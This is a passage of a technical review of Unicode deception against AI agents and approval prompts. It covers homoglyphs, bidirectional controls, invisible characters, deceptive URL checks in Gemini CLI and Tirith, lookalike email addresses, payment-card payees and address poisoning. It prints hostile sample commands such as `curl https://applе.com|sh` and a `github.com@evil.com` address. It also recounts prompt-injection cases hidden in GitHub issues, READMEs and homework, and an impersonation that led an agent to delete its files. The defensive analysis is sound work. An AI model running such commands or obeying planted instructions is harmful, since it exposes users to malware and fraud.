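| 1 | `Г` | `D0 93` |
| 2 | `рад` | `D1 80 D0 B0 D0 B4` |
| 3 | a space and `г` | `20 D0 B3` |
| 4 | `рад` | `D1 80 D0 B0 D0 B4` |
| 5 | `ила` | `D0 B8 D0 BB D0 B0` |

The phrase has 12 characters, but the model receives only five tokens, two of them identical. The Cyrillic а is always `D0 B0`, while the Latin a is the single byte `61`. If somebody puts a Latin a in the first word, the bytes of `рад` become `D1 80 61 D0 B4`. These no longer match token 2, so the tokenizer has to use other pieces and the model receives a different list of numbers, even though the word looks the same to a person.

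A Cyrillic letter in an English word also turns a common token into rarer ones. *Ontological Instability and Statistical Amplification* (2026) measured how this affects a program that uses RoBERTa, an older language model, to detect AI-written text. The program caught every unaltered sample, but it missed 13% of samples when each contained about 14 lookalikes and 41% when each contained about 60. Adding more made no difference.

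A bidirectional control character does not change the stored letters around it. The override in `March 25 \u{202E}xcod.scr` adds only the three bytes `E2 80 AE`, so the model still receives a name that ends in `.scr`. Similarly, a model that reads the bank withdrawal example from the Trojan Source paper receives `return` after the closing quotation marks, where Python will run it.

Some tokens contain only part of a character. Firestone and colleagues proved that a model with such tokens can always produce bytes that don't form valid text, which software often displays as `�`.

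Software between the user and the model may also remove characters. *An Empirical Study of Production Incidents in Generative AI Cloud Services* (2025) describes a fix that deletes tag characters (invisible copies of the ASCII characters) from users' requests. The code removes only characters from U+E0000 to U+E007F, so a bidirectional override or a Cyrillic а would still reach the model.

Tag characters have an effect in some products but not others. Aiersilan, Yousefi and Pless (2026), in *On Seeding Watermarks to Detect Verbatim LLM Copy-Paste Responses*, used them to hide an instruction in homework assignments. The instruction told the model to add a particular code to its answer, which would expose students who pasted the whole assignment into a chatbot. Six of the 13 model configurations tested never added the code. Either something removed the characters before they reached the model,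 or the model received them and didn't act on them.

### GPT models and altered code in 2024

In *What You See Is Not Always What You Get*, Wen, Zhu and Chen (2024) tested whether three OpenAI models could understand code containing deceptive characters. They paired each of 300 JavaScript solutions from LeetCode, a programming practice website, with a description of the problem it solves. The models had to say, yes or no, whether the code matched the description.

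The researchers altered the code in four ways, each meant to leave its appearance unchanged:

- **Reordering:** they stored the beginning of the program backwards and used the right-to-left override to make it display normally.
- **Invisible characters:** they added a zero-width non-joiner after each character.
- **Deletions:** they inserted the letter a followed by a backspace character, which erases the letter on displays that obey it.
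- **Homoglyphs:** they replaced characters with lookalikes from a Unicode Consortium list.

They applied each method to 20%, 40%, 60%, 80% and 100% of the code, which made 1,500 altered prompts per method for each model. For homoglyphs, the percentages covered only the characters that have a suitable lookalike, so this method changed less of the code than the others. Since a person would still see a matching program, the researchers counted only "yes" as correct. The table gives the share of correct answers:

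| Model | Reordering | Invisible characters | Deletions | Homoglyphs |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-3.5 Turbo, June 2023 | 44% | 55% | 34% | 71% |
| GPT-3.5 Turbo, January 2024 | 33% | 58% | 19% | 69% |
| GPT-4o, May 2024 | 0.8% | 1.0% | 0.9% | 0.7% |

All three models answered "yes" every time the code was unaltered. The two older models generally did worse as the alterations increased. With reordering, for example, the June 2023 model fell from 73% correct at the lowest level of alteration to 16% at the highest. GPT-4o answered "no" for nearly all the altered code, even at the lowest level.

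Wen and colleagues concluded that GPT-4o could detect special characters, and that OpenAI had probably added a safeguard that made it answer "no". They acknowledged that their design couldn't show why the model gave an answer. A simpler explanation is that "no" was often right, because a program whose first part is stored backwards won't run, and a model that judges the stored text should reject it.

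The study measured whether a model could recover what a person sees, but someone approving an agent's draft needs to know what the machine will do. The test was also easier in one respect than a Trojan Source attack, where the stored text is valid code and doesn't look broken.

These results are now mainly of historical interest. OpenAI has since released much stronger models, and agents can now run a short program to print the code points in a suspicious line. Chatbots have also become good at reading heavily altered text, according to a May 2026 study of attempts to prevent them from doing so.

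### Familiar questions with one strange digit

*Homoglyph-based Adversarial Perturbation of Introductory Computer Science Theory Problems* (Alexander, Juneja and colleagues, 2026) describes an attempt to write homework that students couldn't solve by pasting it into a chatbot. Replacing letters with lookalikes didn't work at first. ChatGPT and Gemini could still answer a question about rational numbers after the researchers had altered so many of its characters that people found it difficult to read. The chatbots also filled in an important word that the researchers had deleted.

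The question appears in popular textbooks, so the researchers suspected that the chatbots were recalling it from their training data. To exploit this, they changed a detail of a familiar question and wrote the new detail with a lookalike that the chatbots couldn't identify. They found the lookalike by asking the chatbots what a character was.

In a well-known puzzle, the solver must measure 4 gallons of water with an 8-gallon jug and two smaller ones. Researchers replaced the 8 with a character that looks like a 6. A person reads "6-gallon", but Gemini solved the original 8-gallon puzzle. In another question, they changed `x` to `7x`, with a lookalike for the 7. ChatGPT left out the 7 and gave a proof about `x`.

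The researchers tried the method on 69 questions from a discrete mathematics course and eventually fooled both chatbots on all of them. Fooling ChatGPT took 1.5 attempts per question on average and never more than five. Fooling Gemini took 1.7 on average and at most 12. An attempt typically changed about three characters, though changing one was often enough.

The researchers selected characters that the chatbots had already failed to recognise, so these figures measure how easily a persistent person can find a lookalike that works, not how often a model would misread one encountered by chance. The paper names the products but doesn't give the model versions.

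Using more lookalikes sometimes made the method less effective. In a question about adding fractions, the researchers replaced every 1 in a numerator with the same lookalike of 7. ChatGPT read the symbol as π and otherwise solved the problem correctly. When they replaced only one of the 1s, ChatGPT told the user that "a couple of the symbols didn't render correctly", but then treated the symbol as a 1 because that gave a standard problem. It therefore answered a different question from the one on the screen.

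An agent could make the same kind of mistake when it summarises a draft for its user. If a web address contains an unfamiliar letter, the summary might name the well-known site that the address resembles. The user would then have two reasons to trust the address: its appearance and the agent's description. The homework study didn't test this, but its results are a good reason not to rely on a summary alone.

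### Models as reviewers

Many companies now sell AI code review, so it matters whether a model would report these characters. The most direct test is an informal one by the blogger devansh, in *Trojan War against State-of-the-Art LLMs*. It used the bank withdrawal example, in which a hidden `return` leaves Alice with 100 when a reader would expect 50.

ChatGPT, Claude and Grok all worked out the correct balance for a harmless version of the program. devansh then gave the deceptive version to more than ten models, and only Grok 2 passed. The ones that failed included ChatGPT, Claude, GitHub Copilot, DeepSeek R1 and Llama 3.3.

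If each chat window preserved the control character, these models received `return` outside the docstring and still treated it as part of the description. They may have relied on what such a function normally does, as Gemini did with the jugs. But the test used only one program, and predicting a program's output is a different task from looking for hidden characters. The post is undated, and the models it tested date from around the beginning of 2025.

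In *LLM Code Reviewers Are Harder to Fool Than You Think*, Thornton (2026) tested whether a different kind of deception, misleading code comments, would fool newer models, including Claude Opus 4.6 and GPT-5.2. The benchmark has 100 code samples in Python, JavaScript and Java, each with eight versions of its comments. One misleading comment states that a security team has already audited the code. As the title indicates, such comments were not very effective.

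This is encouraging because Trojan Source attacks also use comments to mislead reviewers. But Thornton's comments mislead through their wording. To catch a Trojan Source attack, a model must also work out exactly where a comment ends, and to catch a homoglyph, it must notice that two names differ by one letter.

There seems to be no published test of whether current models report bidirectional controls or homoglyphs in code they review. They should be better at this than the models devansh tried, particularly when they can run programs. *Reverse CAPTCHA* (Graves, 2026) found that five models followed invisible instructions in at most 1.1% of cases without tools or hints, but that the most susceptible did so in 98% to 100% of cases when they could run code and had directions for decoding the text. Graves was measuring a weakness, but the same ability could help a reviewer. A model with a code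 tool and explicit instructions to check for unusual characters would probably find more of them than one that only reads the code.

Even so, a short script is more dependable for finding these characters. curl's check finds every byte outside ASCII, apart from its listed exceptions, and gives the same result each time. A model is more useful for deciding whether a character the script has found belongs there. For example, it can recognise that a Hebrew comment needs Hebrew letters, while a lone Cyrillic letter in an English function name needs an explanation. The same division of work would suit products that use a model to approve an agent's actions automatically.

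### How the characters enter a draft

Most simply, an agent may copy these characters into its output along with a name from a web page or a block of code from a repository. Homoglyphs are widespread on social media, according to *Data interference* (2025), so an agent can come across them even where nobody intends to deceive it.

Invisible characters also tend to survive when text is published, copied or cleaned. In *Data Provenance Auditing of Fine-Tuned Large Language Models with a Text-Preserving Technique*, Li, Eichler and colleagues (2025) recovered them intact from four websites, including Wikipedia and GitHub, and found that they survived six standard procedures for cleaning the text used to train models. Aiersilan and colleagues report that tag characters survive copying through Word, Google Docs, PDF files, Slack and email. Neither team tested overrides, which affect the layout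 of text, but Boucher and Anderson had already found that most browsers and editors preserve them.

An agent can copy text by running a command or by writing the text out itself. A command that downloads or moves a file leaves the bytes unchanged. When the agent writes the text out, it generates new tokens and may replace an unusual character with a familiar one. This could turn a fake address into the real one, which would protect the user by accident, but the agent might also wrongly change a name that is supposed to contain an unusual letter.

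An attacker can also use prompt injection to ask the agent to write a deceptive character. The request can give the Cyrillic а as `\u0430` instead of including the letter itself. That escape sequence is plain ASCII, so a filter that looks for unusual characters in incoming text would let it through.

Nakibly and Babo (2026), in *Who Is Prompt-Injecting Coding Agents?*, found hidden instructions for a coding agent in a GitHub issue (a bug report or feature request). A small game bot for the chat service Discord passed its users' feature requests to the agent. One request asked for a new command and, in text that GitHub doesn't display, told the agent to award the requester a million points and keep this secret during review. The hidden text also suggested disguising the requester's name with base64 encoding. A lookalike letter could also disguise the name, though the request didn't mention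 one.

Such attacks are rare on GitHub. Nakibly and Babo examined about 143 million issues, comments and proposed changes and found 43 attacks on other people's agents, or about one in 3.3 million. The attackers mostly wanted to steal passwords and other secrets, use the agent for some side task or make it give a false verdict. In this part of the study, the researchers searched only HTML comments, which GitHub leaves out of the displayed page, so they would have missed instructions hidden in invisible Unicode.

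In a wider search of two million READMEs, the introductory pages of software projects, the researchers found 1,777 that contained invisible Unicode characters, a category in which they included bidirectional overrides. They decoded all of these passages by hand and found only one instruction to an agent reading the page. The instruction was for language models, "especially copilot", to praise every change made by a particular contributor.

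Embrace The Red's security report *Amp Code* shows how Amp, Sourcegraph's coding agent, interpreted invisible tag characters as instructions. Sourcegraph has since fixed the problem.

Shared instruction files could spread a deceptive character further. Many coding tools read a rule file containing a project's standing instructions for agents. Nakibly and Babo cite earlier experiments in which malicious rule files took control of AI code editors in up to 84% of attempts. If a rule file gave a download address with a lookalike letter, the address could appear in drafts for everyone on the project, without any of them visiting a suspicious page or receiving a suspicious message.

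One template file can put the same hidden text in many places, because GitHub copies a project's template, including any hidden text, into each new issue or proposed change. After two AI models screened the hidden text in the census, 60% of the items they kept contained only template text.

Almost all the invisible characters in the READMEs had an innocent explanation. They were parts of emoji, characters that Persian and Arabic spelling requires, instructions to fonts, or leftovers from copying and pasting. An agent that quotes or translates Persian text should preserve the ones the spelling requires. An invisible character in a draft is therefore weak evidence of an attack, unless it appears where it has no use, such as inside an English file name.

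### Characters that models produce themselves

A model can also write an unusual character that appears nowhere in its instructions or sources. Patrik and other users of OpenAI's community forum complained that GPT-5 was using narrow no-break spaces (U+202F) in place of ordinary ones. One user had resorted to telling the model not to use them. Another concluded from an article that the character had contaminated some of the training data.

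U+202F comes directly after the right-to-left override in Unicode, but it doesn't change the order of the text. In prose, it only makes the words look slightly cramped. It can do more harm in a terminal command, where it looks like a space but doesn't separate words.

Li and colleagues trained models to reproduce invisible characters as a way to prove that someone had used a document for training. They put a sequence of these characters in each document they marked, trained two small open models on the whole collection, and then prompted the models with the first half of the sequence. The models completed the sequence at a rate of more than 28% per document, even when only 40 documents, or 4% of the collection, were marked. The researchers had repeated the sequence throughout each marked document, so a model is much less likely to learn a stray character that appears once.

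Nobody appears to have published a count of how often agents copy or write bidirectional controls or homoglyphs. The GitHub census covers text that agents might read but not text they produce. The forum complaints concern one harmless space character and give no rate. Researchers could measure this by giving agents web pages and repositories that contain known instances of these characters, then searching the agents' drafts for the same code points. They could also repeat GitHub's 2021 search for Trojan Source attacks, but only on changes that agents wrote.

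## Gemini CLI's warning about deceptive web addresses

Gemini CLI, Google's coding agent for the terminal, normally asks for permission before it fetches a web page or runs a command. Since February 2026, these prompts have also shown a warning if a web address has a suspicious host name. Ordinary code produces the warning, so it doesn't depend on the model detecting a strange letter.

The developer ehedlund (2026) proposed the feature on 17 February in the pull request *security* (a pull request is a change submitted for a project's maintainers to accept or reject).

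### How the check works

The proposed code checks an approval prompt in five steps:

1. It collects the addresses. A web request comes with a list of them. In a command, the code looks for `http://` or `https://` and takes everything up to the next space, quotation mark, backtick or angle bracket.
2. It removes duplicates.
3. It splits each address into its parts, following the same standard as browsers, to find the host name. This also converts an international name to Punycode.
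4. It checks whether the host name contains a Punycode label or any character outside ASCII.
5. If so, it adds a warning with two fields, "Original" and "Actual Host (Punycode)". Several suspicious addresses share one warning.

The code also calculates how many lines the warning needs, so that a small terminal window doesn't cut it off.

For web requests, the prompt lists addresses in Unicode, even if the agent wrote them in Punycode. This helps people who read Japanese or Russian names, but it also turns the odd-looking `xn--80ak6aa92e.com` back into the convincing `аррӏе.com`. An automated review of a later pull request praised this conversion for letting users inspect the real domain. But the Unicode form of a lookalike is what deceives people, so the user's protection comes from the warning rather than the conversion.

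### Five addresses

The table shows the result of working through these steps by hand for five addresses in a command.

| Address in the command | Host name after conversion | Warning |
|---|---|---|
| `https://apple.com/setup.sh` | `apple.com` | No |
| `https://applе.com/setup.sh`, with a Cyrillic е | `xn--appl-y4d.com` | Yes |
| `https://münchen.de/setup.sh` | `xn--mnchen-3ya.de` | Yes |
| `https://rnicrosoft.com/setup.sh` | `rnicrosoft.com` | No |
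| `applе.com/setup.sh`, with a Cyrillic е | The code doesn't extract the address | No |

The check is right about the first two addresses and wrong about the other three. `münchen.de` is a legitimate name that uses the German spelling of Munich, and rsurl, a version of curl written in Rust, uses it as its example of an international host. The check doesn't flag `rnicrosoft.com` because the name is all ASCII.

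The most worrying failure is that the pattern misses addresses without `https://`, because an attacker can exploit this by leaving out a few characters. curl assumes `http://` when they are missing, so `curl -O applе.com/setup.sh` still contacts the lookalike site. The pattern also skips `ssh://` addresses and the `git@` form that programmers use to download repositories. A broader pattern would cause new false alarms. For example, the Russian file name `заметки.md` ("notes.md") has the same form as a web address under Moldova's domain, `.md`.

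When the code does extract an address, its simple rule catches some tricks that got past browsers. It would flag Zheng's all-Cyrillic `аррӏе.com`, the fake Chrome Web Store address that uses the Japanese letter ん as a false slash, and the Hebrew domain that swaps places with its path. The rule covers the whole host name, including subdomains, and doesn't depend on which scripts are combined. It misses real government names that criminals use as subdomains, since those are ASCII.

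### Edits, questions and saved permissions

Gemini Code Assist, Google's AI code reviewer, found a gap in the pull request and rated it high severity. The check covered web requests and commands, but an agent can also put a deceptive address in a file edit or in a question to the user. The reviewer supplied code to search file edits and questions too.

In the curl test, Fuller swapped a letter in a web address inside a script. If an agent made the same change, Gemini CLI would ask the user to approve a file edit without running the check. The agent might later ask to run the script with a command such as `sh update.sh`. That command contains no web address, so the user would get no warning then either.

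The warning is also limited to permission prompts. Gemini CLI's release notes describe an "Always Allow" option, added in December 2025, that saves a user's permission for particular commands. Someone who has permanently allowed `curl` would presumably see neither the prompt nor the warning.

### From the proposal to the current version

ehedlund closed the pull request on the day it opened and replaced it with another, #19288, which left out some unrelated changes. NewReleases lists the replacement in version 0.31.0, which Google released on 27 February. The same version began removing deceptive Unicode characters from terminal output.

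On 20 February the project also accepted pull request #19689, *fix(core): restore auth consent in headless mode and add unit tests* (ehedlund, 2026), which mainly repaired sign-in for sessions without an interactive screen. Its automated summary also describes the address check, which still covered only web requests and commands. The code did not yet include the reviewer's suggestion about edits and questions.

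One detail had improved. The extraction now stops at shell delimiters, the symbols that separate commands. Consider this command, which downloads a script and runs it immediately:

`curl https://applе.com|sh`

The original pattern would have treated `applе.com|sh` as the host name. A vertical bar isn't valid in a host name, so the address would have failed to parse, and the function described in the summary gives no warning when parsing fails. An attacker could probably have avoided the original check by leaving out the two spaces around the bar.

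The highlights in Gemini CLI's release notes mention no change to the warning up to version 0.54.0 in August. Google still maintains the program, and Releasebot's *Gemini CLI Updates & Release Notes* lists version 0.63.0 in September.

Fewer people can now use Gemini CLI. It stopped serving individual users, including AI Pro and AI Ultra subscribers, on 18 June, according to Google's *Gemini Code Assist consumer accounts*. Google directed them to its Antigravity products. Virtualization Review's *Google Moves Gemini CLI into Antigravity CLI as Agent Platform Expands* (2026) reported that organisations with Standard or Enterprise licences and users with paid API keys would keep access.

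The changelog for Antigravity's command-line agent lists no warning about deceptive addresses up to version 1.0.13. The agent may still have one, since a changelog might not mention a feature that was there from the start. But people who switched from Gemini CLI may no longer have this protection.

### Tirith: a check in the shell

Tirith is an open-source program that checks commands in the shell, the program that runs what someone types in a terminal. Its GitHub page opens with the slogan "Your browser would catch this. Your terminal won't." Tirith's developer, sheeki, first submitted it to a community collection of software for Arch Linux on 3 February 2026, according to AUR's *Package Details* (2026).

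Tirith installs a hook, a piece of code that the shell runs when the user presses Enter. The hook examines the command and lets it through, prints a warning or blocks it. In the project's main example, it blocks a download from `іnstall.example-clі.dev`, which has two Cyrillic letters in place of the Latin i. Users who trust a site can add it to a list of exceptions, or put `TIRITH=0` in front of a command to skip the check once. Organisations can disable this bypass, which is sensible if they run agents, because an agent can add the prefix too.

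The source code of Tirith 0.3.0 shows how it would treat the five test addresses. It would not flag the host `apple.com`, but it would rate the version with a Cyrillic е as a high risk. It would give `münchen.de` the same rating, for both the ü and the Punycode form. In the project's examples, a high rating blocks the command until the user makes an exception, so this false alarm is more disruptive than Gemini CLI's.

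Tirith does better with `rnicrosoft.com`. It replaces letter combinations that people misread, such as rn for m, and compares the result with a list of known domains. If `microsoft.com` is on the list, Tirith warns the user. It also warns about names that differ from a known domain by one edit, but skips this test for very short domains because it would produce too many false alarms.

In an address without `https://`, recent versions of Tirith look for single words that mix scripts. This should catch `applе.com` but not the all-Cyrillic `аррӏе.com`.

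Another rule covers addresses like `http://github.com@evil.com/`, which opens `evil.com` because the text before the @ is only a user name. Gemini CLI's check would miss this address because its host is plain ASCII.

Some of Tirith's rules are broad. Version 0.3.0 warns about every address ending in `.dev`, `.app`, `.zip`, `.mov` or `.run`, because people might confuse these endings with file extensions. The address labeled "safe" in the project's own example ends in `.dev`, so it would get a warning too.

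Tirith also protects agents less broadly than its documentation once said. When Tirith had 66 rules, the documentation said that any tool that starts a shell would inherit the protection. The corrected documentation for version 0.4.1, which has 244 rules, says that the hook covers only commands that pass through an interactive shell in which it is loaded. Agents commonly start a non-interactive shell or launch a program directly, and the hook doesn't check those commands.

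For such agents, Tirith can connect to the agent's own system for checking actions before they run. This protection depends on the agent, since Cline, OpenHands and Grok Build go ahead with the action if the check crashes or times out. Tirith blocks reliably in the zsh and fish shells but can only warn in nushell, and in bash the result depends on the mode.

Where both protections work, the user sees Gemini CLI's warning before deciding whether to approve a command, and Tirith can still stop the command after the user approves it.

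### False alarms on honest names

Both tools treat every international host name as suspicious, but most of these names are harmless. The Unicode Consortium gives `Bücher.de` ("books" in German) as an ordinary example. DShield's *Getting a Better Handle on International Domain Names and Punycode* argues that such names are probably less of a problem than some people suggest, and that mixed scripts are the more interesting sign. ICANN's figures suggest that international names are rarely malicious.

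False alarms can also make a real attack harder to notice. Suppose a developer in Munich often approves downloads from `münchen.de` and sees Gemini CLI's warning each time. An attacker then registers the name with a Cyrillic е. The prompt shows the same kind of warning as before, and only the code is different:

```
honest name:       xn--mnchen-3ya.de
with Cyrillic е:   xn--mnchn-kva298c.de
```

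Few people would remember the first code well enough to notice the change. The warning works well for someone who expects `apple.com`, because any Punycode is a sign of trouble, but it is much less useful to the developer in Munich.

A narrower rule that flagged only mixed scripts would tell the two Munich names apart, but it would miss the all-Cyrillic `аррӏе.com`. Chromium's rules cover both kinds of lookalike but require a long series of checks. Gemini CLI's rule needs no list of lookalikes and no knowledge of fonts, so the discovery of a new lookalike can't make it out of date.

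That simplicity is worth having in an approval prompt because the user has already stopped to decide, and a false alarm delays them by only a few seconds. It is harder to justify in Tirith, where the same false alarm blocks the command.

The wording is the weakest part of Gemini CLI's design, because ehedlund chose the term "Deceptive URL" for every name the rule catches. LangChain, which makes software for building agents, uses a more graded approach. Its *unicode security* describes a small set of checks that developers can build into approval screens. In its *UrlSafetyResult*, an address can count as safe and still carry a note, for example that it contains Punycode. Gemini CLI could likewise show the actual host for every international name but call it deceptive only if it mixes scripts suspiciously or consists entirely of lookalikes. The developer in Munich would then see a quiet note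 for the real `münchen.de` and a much stronger warning for the fake one.

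## Recipient addresses and payee names in drafted messages and payments

An agent that emails a contract to the wrong person can't get it back, and many payments are just as hard to reverse. The approval prompt is often the user's last chance to notice a wrong recipient. In a drafted email, the recipient might look like this:

`"Anna Berg" <anna@example.com>`

- `Anna Berg` is the display name, a label for people to read.
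- `anna` is the local part, which identifies a mailbox.
- `example.com` is the domain, which tells the sender's mail server where to deliver the message.

Email addresses originally contained only ASCII characters. In 2012 the Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF), which publishes many of the internet's technical standards, opened them to other scripts so that people could spell their own names correctly. The main standards are RFC 6530, 6531 and 6532. Yang, Steele and Freed (2012), in *Internationalized Email Headers*, and Yao and Mao (2012), in *SMTP Extension for Internationalized Email*, set out which characters each part can carry:

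| Part | Characters outside ASCII | What interprets it |
|---|---|---|
| Display name | Almost any | The person reading it |
| Local part | Almost any | The receiving mail server |
| Domain | Those that the rules for internationalized domain names allow | The domain name system |

### A familiar name on an unfamiliar address

Mail servers deliver a message according to its envelope, a set of delivery instructions separate from the header that people read. According to Klensin and Ko (2012), in *Overview and Framework for Internationalized Email*, the envelope doesn't contain the display name. Whoever writes the header can therefore put any name beside any address:

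```
known contact:   "Anna Berg" <anna@example.com>
in the draft:    "Anna Berg" <aberg@post.example>
```

If the approval prompt shows only the display name, two recipients with the same name look identical, even when the draft contains no unusual characters. An attacker can also use the intended recipient's address as the display name, as in `"anna@example.com" <aberg@post.example>`. The simplest defence is to show the full address in every prompt.

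Display names can also contain bidirectional control characters, although the Unicode Consortium's rules allow only direction marks there. Gulbrandsen and Yao (2026) warn in *Interoperable Email Addresses for SMTPUTF8* that text from an attacker can change how a surprisingly large part of the surrounding line appears, and mention display names and subject lines as places where an attacker can insert such text.

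Display names can deceive agents too. *Approve What, Exactly?* (Kodathala, Pollishetty and Cargill, 2026) recounts a case from *Agents of Chaos*, a two-week study in which researchers attacked working agents. Someone changed their Discord display name to that of an agent's owner and opened a private channel. The agent concluded from the name and tone that this was its owner, then deleted its own memory and configuration files and reassigned administrative access.

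### Why the part before the @ has no Punycode

The next two examples replace a Latin a with a Cyrillic а, one in the domain and the other in the local part. On screen, both look like `anna@example.com`.

```
lookalike domain:       anna@ex\u{0430}mple.com
with domain in ASCII:   anna@xn--exmple-4nf.com

lookalike local part:   \u{0430}nna@example.com
with domain in ASCII:   \u{0430}nna@example.com
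```

Converting the domain to Punycode exposes the first address and does nothing for the second, because its domain is the real one.

Mail servers look up an address's domain in the domain name system, so the domain has the same Punycode form everywhere, and an approval prompt can show that form. There is no shared directory of local parts, the text before the @ sign. Only the receiving server decides which mailbox a local part refers to, and the basic email standard forbids other servers from interpreting it.

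In Klensin and Ko's example, `user%foo@example.com`, the server at `example.com` might treat `user%foo` as an ordinary mailbox or as an instruction to forward the message to `user` by way of `foo`. Other servers cannot determine which. If a server along the way rewrote the local part in ASCII, the message could reach a different mailbox or none.

The IETF's earlier, experimental standards in effect required each non-ASCII email address to come with an all-ASCII alternative. This raised a security concern because nothing proved that the two addresses belonged together. The working group abandoned the idea after trials showed that different mail systems had trouble working with one another.

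An approval prompt can still escape the local part for display, because the displayed text doesn't have to match the address the mail program uses. It could show `\u{0430}nna@example.com` beside the address, or a note that the first letter is Cyrillic.

A lookalike local part is harder to set up than a lookalike domain because the attacker needs a mailbox at the real contact's domain. A small firm that assigns addresses is unlikely to hand out a Cyrillic `аnna`, but a large provider that lets users choose them might. Klensin and Ko draw the same distinction between small and large mail systems. The receiving server must also support the 2012 standards, because Yao and Mao forbid mail programs to send a non-ASCII local part to a server that doesn't. A lookalike domain doesn't need this support, since its Punycode form is plain ASCII.

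Lowercasing helps reveal lookalike letters in domains. For example, it turns `PayPaI`, which ends in a capital I, into `paypai`. It isn't safe for the local part of an address, because a server may treat `Anna` and `anna` as different mailboxes.

Some lookalikes are accidental. The name `josé` can end in a single character (U+00E9) or in a plain e followed by a separate accent (U+0301). Yang and colleagues recommend NFC, a form of normalization that would use the single character here. They advise against the broader NFKC because it can remove details that matter in some names. Neither form changes the fake `anna`.

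### Two drafts of stricter rules

The IETF is considering a narrower set of addresses. Gulbrandsen and Yao (2026), in *SMTPUTF8 Email Addresses*, propose four simple rules for all mail software. Their companion draft, *Interoperable Email Addresses for SMTPUTF8*, has stricter rules meant mainly for systems that hand out addresses. Working through both sets of rules gives these results, with `ABC` and `DEF` standing for Hebrew letters:

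| Address | Simple rules | Stricter rules |
|---|---|---|
| `admin\u{3164}@example.com`, with an invisible Korean filler | Reject | Reject |
| `\u{0430}nna@example.com` | Accept | Reject |
| `anna@ex\u{0430}mple.com` | Accept | Reject |
| `ABC@DEF.com` | Accept | Reject |
| `info@dømi.fo`, an honest address | Accept | Accept |

The simple draft allows only one script per address but doesn't count ASCII characters. In the fake `anna`, it counts only the Cyrillic а, so the address passes. The stricter draft counts the ASCII letters as Latin and finds two scripts.

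The Hebrew address is a problem of order. In a left-to-right field, the Bidirectional Algorithm reverses everything up to the full stop:

```
stored order:     ABC@DEF.com
displayed order:  FED@CBA.com
```

The message goes to the mailbox `ABC` at `DEF.com`, but a reader who looks to the right of the @ sees `ABC.com`. An attacker who owns `DEF.com` can choose any local part, including the name of a trusted company. Gulbrandsen and Yao describe the same kind of mix-up in signed messages, where a different domain can appear to have signed.

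The stricter rules would catch most of the tricks in this section, but they also reject `анна@example.com`, which could be the legitimate address of someone named Anna who spells her name in Russian. Gulbrandsen and Yao argue that organisations generally assign addresses in the script of their own domain. That may be true of employers, but it is less convincing for public mail providers, whose users come from many countries. The stricter draft expired in September 2026, while the simple one was still under discussion in October.

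Both drafts forbid `xn--` labels inside an address, although the simple draft lists as an open question whether the ban should be firm. Gulbrandsen and Yao think these labels confuse many readers. To expose a lookalike domain, a prompt should therefore show the domain's ASCII form beside the unchanged address.

### The payee name on a sample payment card

A payment also has a name that people read and an identifier that machines use. In the Agent Payments Protocol (AP2), Google's specification for purchases by agents, the user signs a mandate, a digital record of what the agent may buy, after seeing its contents on an approval card. Some mandates instead set limits for later purchases, such as which merchants the agent may pay.

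Kodathala and colleagues ran AP2's checks on mandates and read the source code of its sample card. The card shows `payee.name`, a name that the merchant chooses, but the mandate binds the payment to `payee.id`, an identifier. The card sets no maximum length for the name and does nothing about invisible characters. Two different merchants can therefore look the same:

| | `payee.name` | `payee.id` | What the card shows |
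|---|---|---|---|
| Real shop | Lakeside Books | `merchant-4821` | Lakeside Books |
| Impostor | Lakeside Books | `merchant-9377` | Lakeside Books |

Suppose, in this invented example, that a misleading web page sends the agent to the impostor. The user sees the expected name and signs, and the money goes to `merchant-9377`. The impostor needs no special characters if it can register the same name. If a payment service refused duplicate names, the impostor could add an invisible character or substitute a lookalike Cyrillic letter, and the name on the card would still look right.

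Kodathala and colleagues call this a flaw of the sample card and find no fault with the signed mandate, which prevents anyone from changing the payee after the user signs. If a mandate allows only `merchant-4821`, a payment to `merchant-9377` fails whatever name the impostor uses. The card is sample code that companies can replace, and under AP2's specification they are already supposed to show the mandate on a trusted surface.

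The distinction is fair and helps developers see what to repair, but the user has still signed proof of agreeing to pay an identifier that the card didn't show. Kodathala and colleagues cite a separate 2026 analysis of AP2, in which Aviv and colleagues argue that a valid signature doesn't guarantee that a payment reflects what the user wanted. European payment rules aim to prevent such a gap by requiring that the payer see the amount and the payee, and that the authentication code stop working if either changes, but showing a name serves that purpose only if the name belongs to one payee.

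Printing `merchant-9377` under the name would make the two cards different, but few people know their bookshop's identifier. A warning that says "You have not paid this merchant before" is easier to judge. The software must keep its payment history by identifier for this to work, because a history kept by name would match the impostor to the real merchant's past payments and the warning would not appear.

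### Address poisoning uses ordinary characters

Cryptocurrency users face a similar trick called address poisoning, which involves neither homoglyphs nor reordering. An Ethereum address has 40 hexadecimal digits after `0x`, and wallet software often shows only the first and last few. These two invented addresses look the same in that form:

```
real:       0x7a3f5d208be146c9f0732ad815be9c64e83b91c4
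attacker:   0x7a3fc81602f97b3ea5d460e79f12d83c4b0591c4
shortened:  0x7a3f…91c4
```

The attacker generates addresses until one matches at both ends. Matching eight digits takes about 4.3 billion attempts on average, which a graphics card can manage. The attacker then makes a tiny transfer that puts the address into the victim's payment history and waits for the victim to copy it. An agent that looks up "the address I paid last time" could make the same mistake.

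The attacker's address contains only plain ASCII characters and, in full, doesn't resemble the real one, so escaping, Punycode and the skeleton test don't flag it. The remedy is to show the whole address and have software compare every digit with a saved copy. Showing the whole address doesn't help a reader spot a Cyrillic `аnna`, but an exact comparison by software works in both cases.

### Four checks, tried on a lookalike and an honest stranger

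An approval prompt can protect users without detecting any particular trick. A good check should stop an address that imitates a known contact without making it too hard to write to someone new.

| Check | Lookalike of a known contact | Honest new contact |
|---|---|---|
| Choose the recipient from saved contacts | Stops it, unless somebody has already saved the lookalike | The user must save the contact first |
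| Flag a first-time recipient | Flags it, whichever part is fake | Gives the same flag |
| Show the domain in ASCII | Exposes foreign letters in the domain only | Harmless for most addresses, but `dømi.fo` becomes `xn--dmi-0na.fo` |
| Trace the address to the user's request | Flags it if it came from a web page or message | Passes if the user typed it, but not if the agent found it |

Limiting recipients to saved contacts is the strictest safeguard. The agent names a contact and the mail program fills in the address, so text from a web page can't supply a recipient. This suits payments to regular suppliers, but the user still has to find the right address when saving a new contact.

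The first-time flag covers the most cases, including a Cyrillic letter on either side of the @, `rn` in place of m, and an impostor with a different `payee.id`. The approval system that Kodathala and colleagues built applies such a check to every recipient, after lowercasing email addresses and converting their domains to ASCII. A program that runs this check should also normalize accents, or it will flag the second spelling of `josé` as a new recipient.

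A check for first-time recipients should treat an address as familiar only if the user has deliberately written to it or paid it. If the check accepts every address in the user's history, an attacker can defeat it by adding an address to that history. In address poisoning, the attacker does this by sending the user a tiny transfer, and an email could do the same in the user's inbox.

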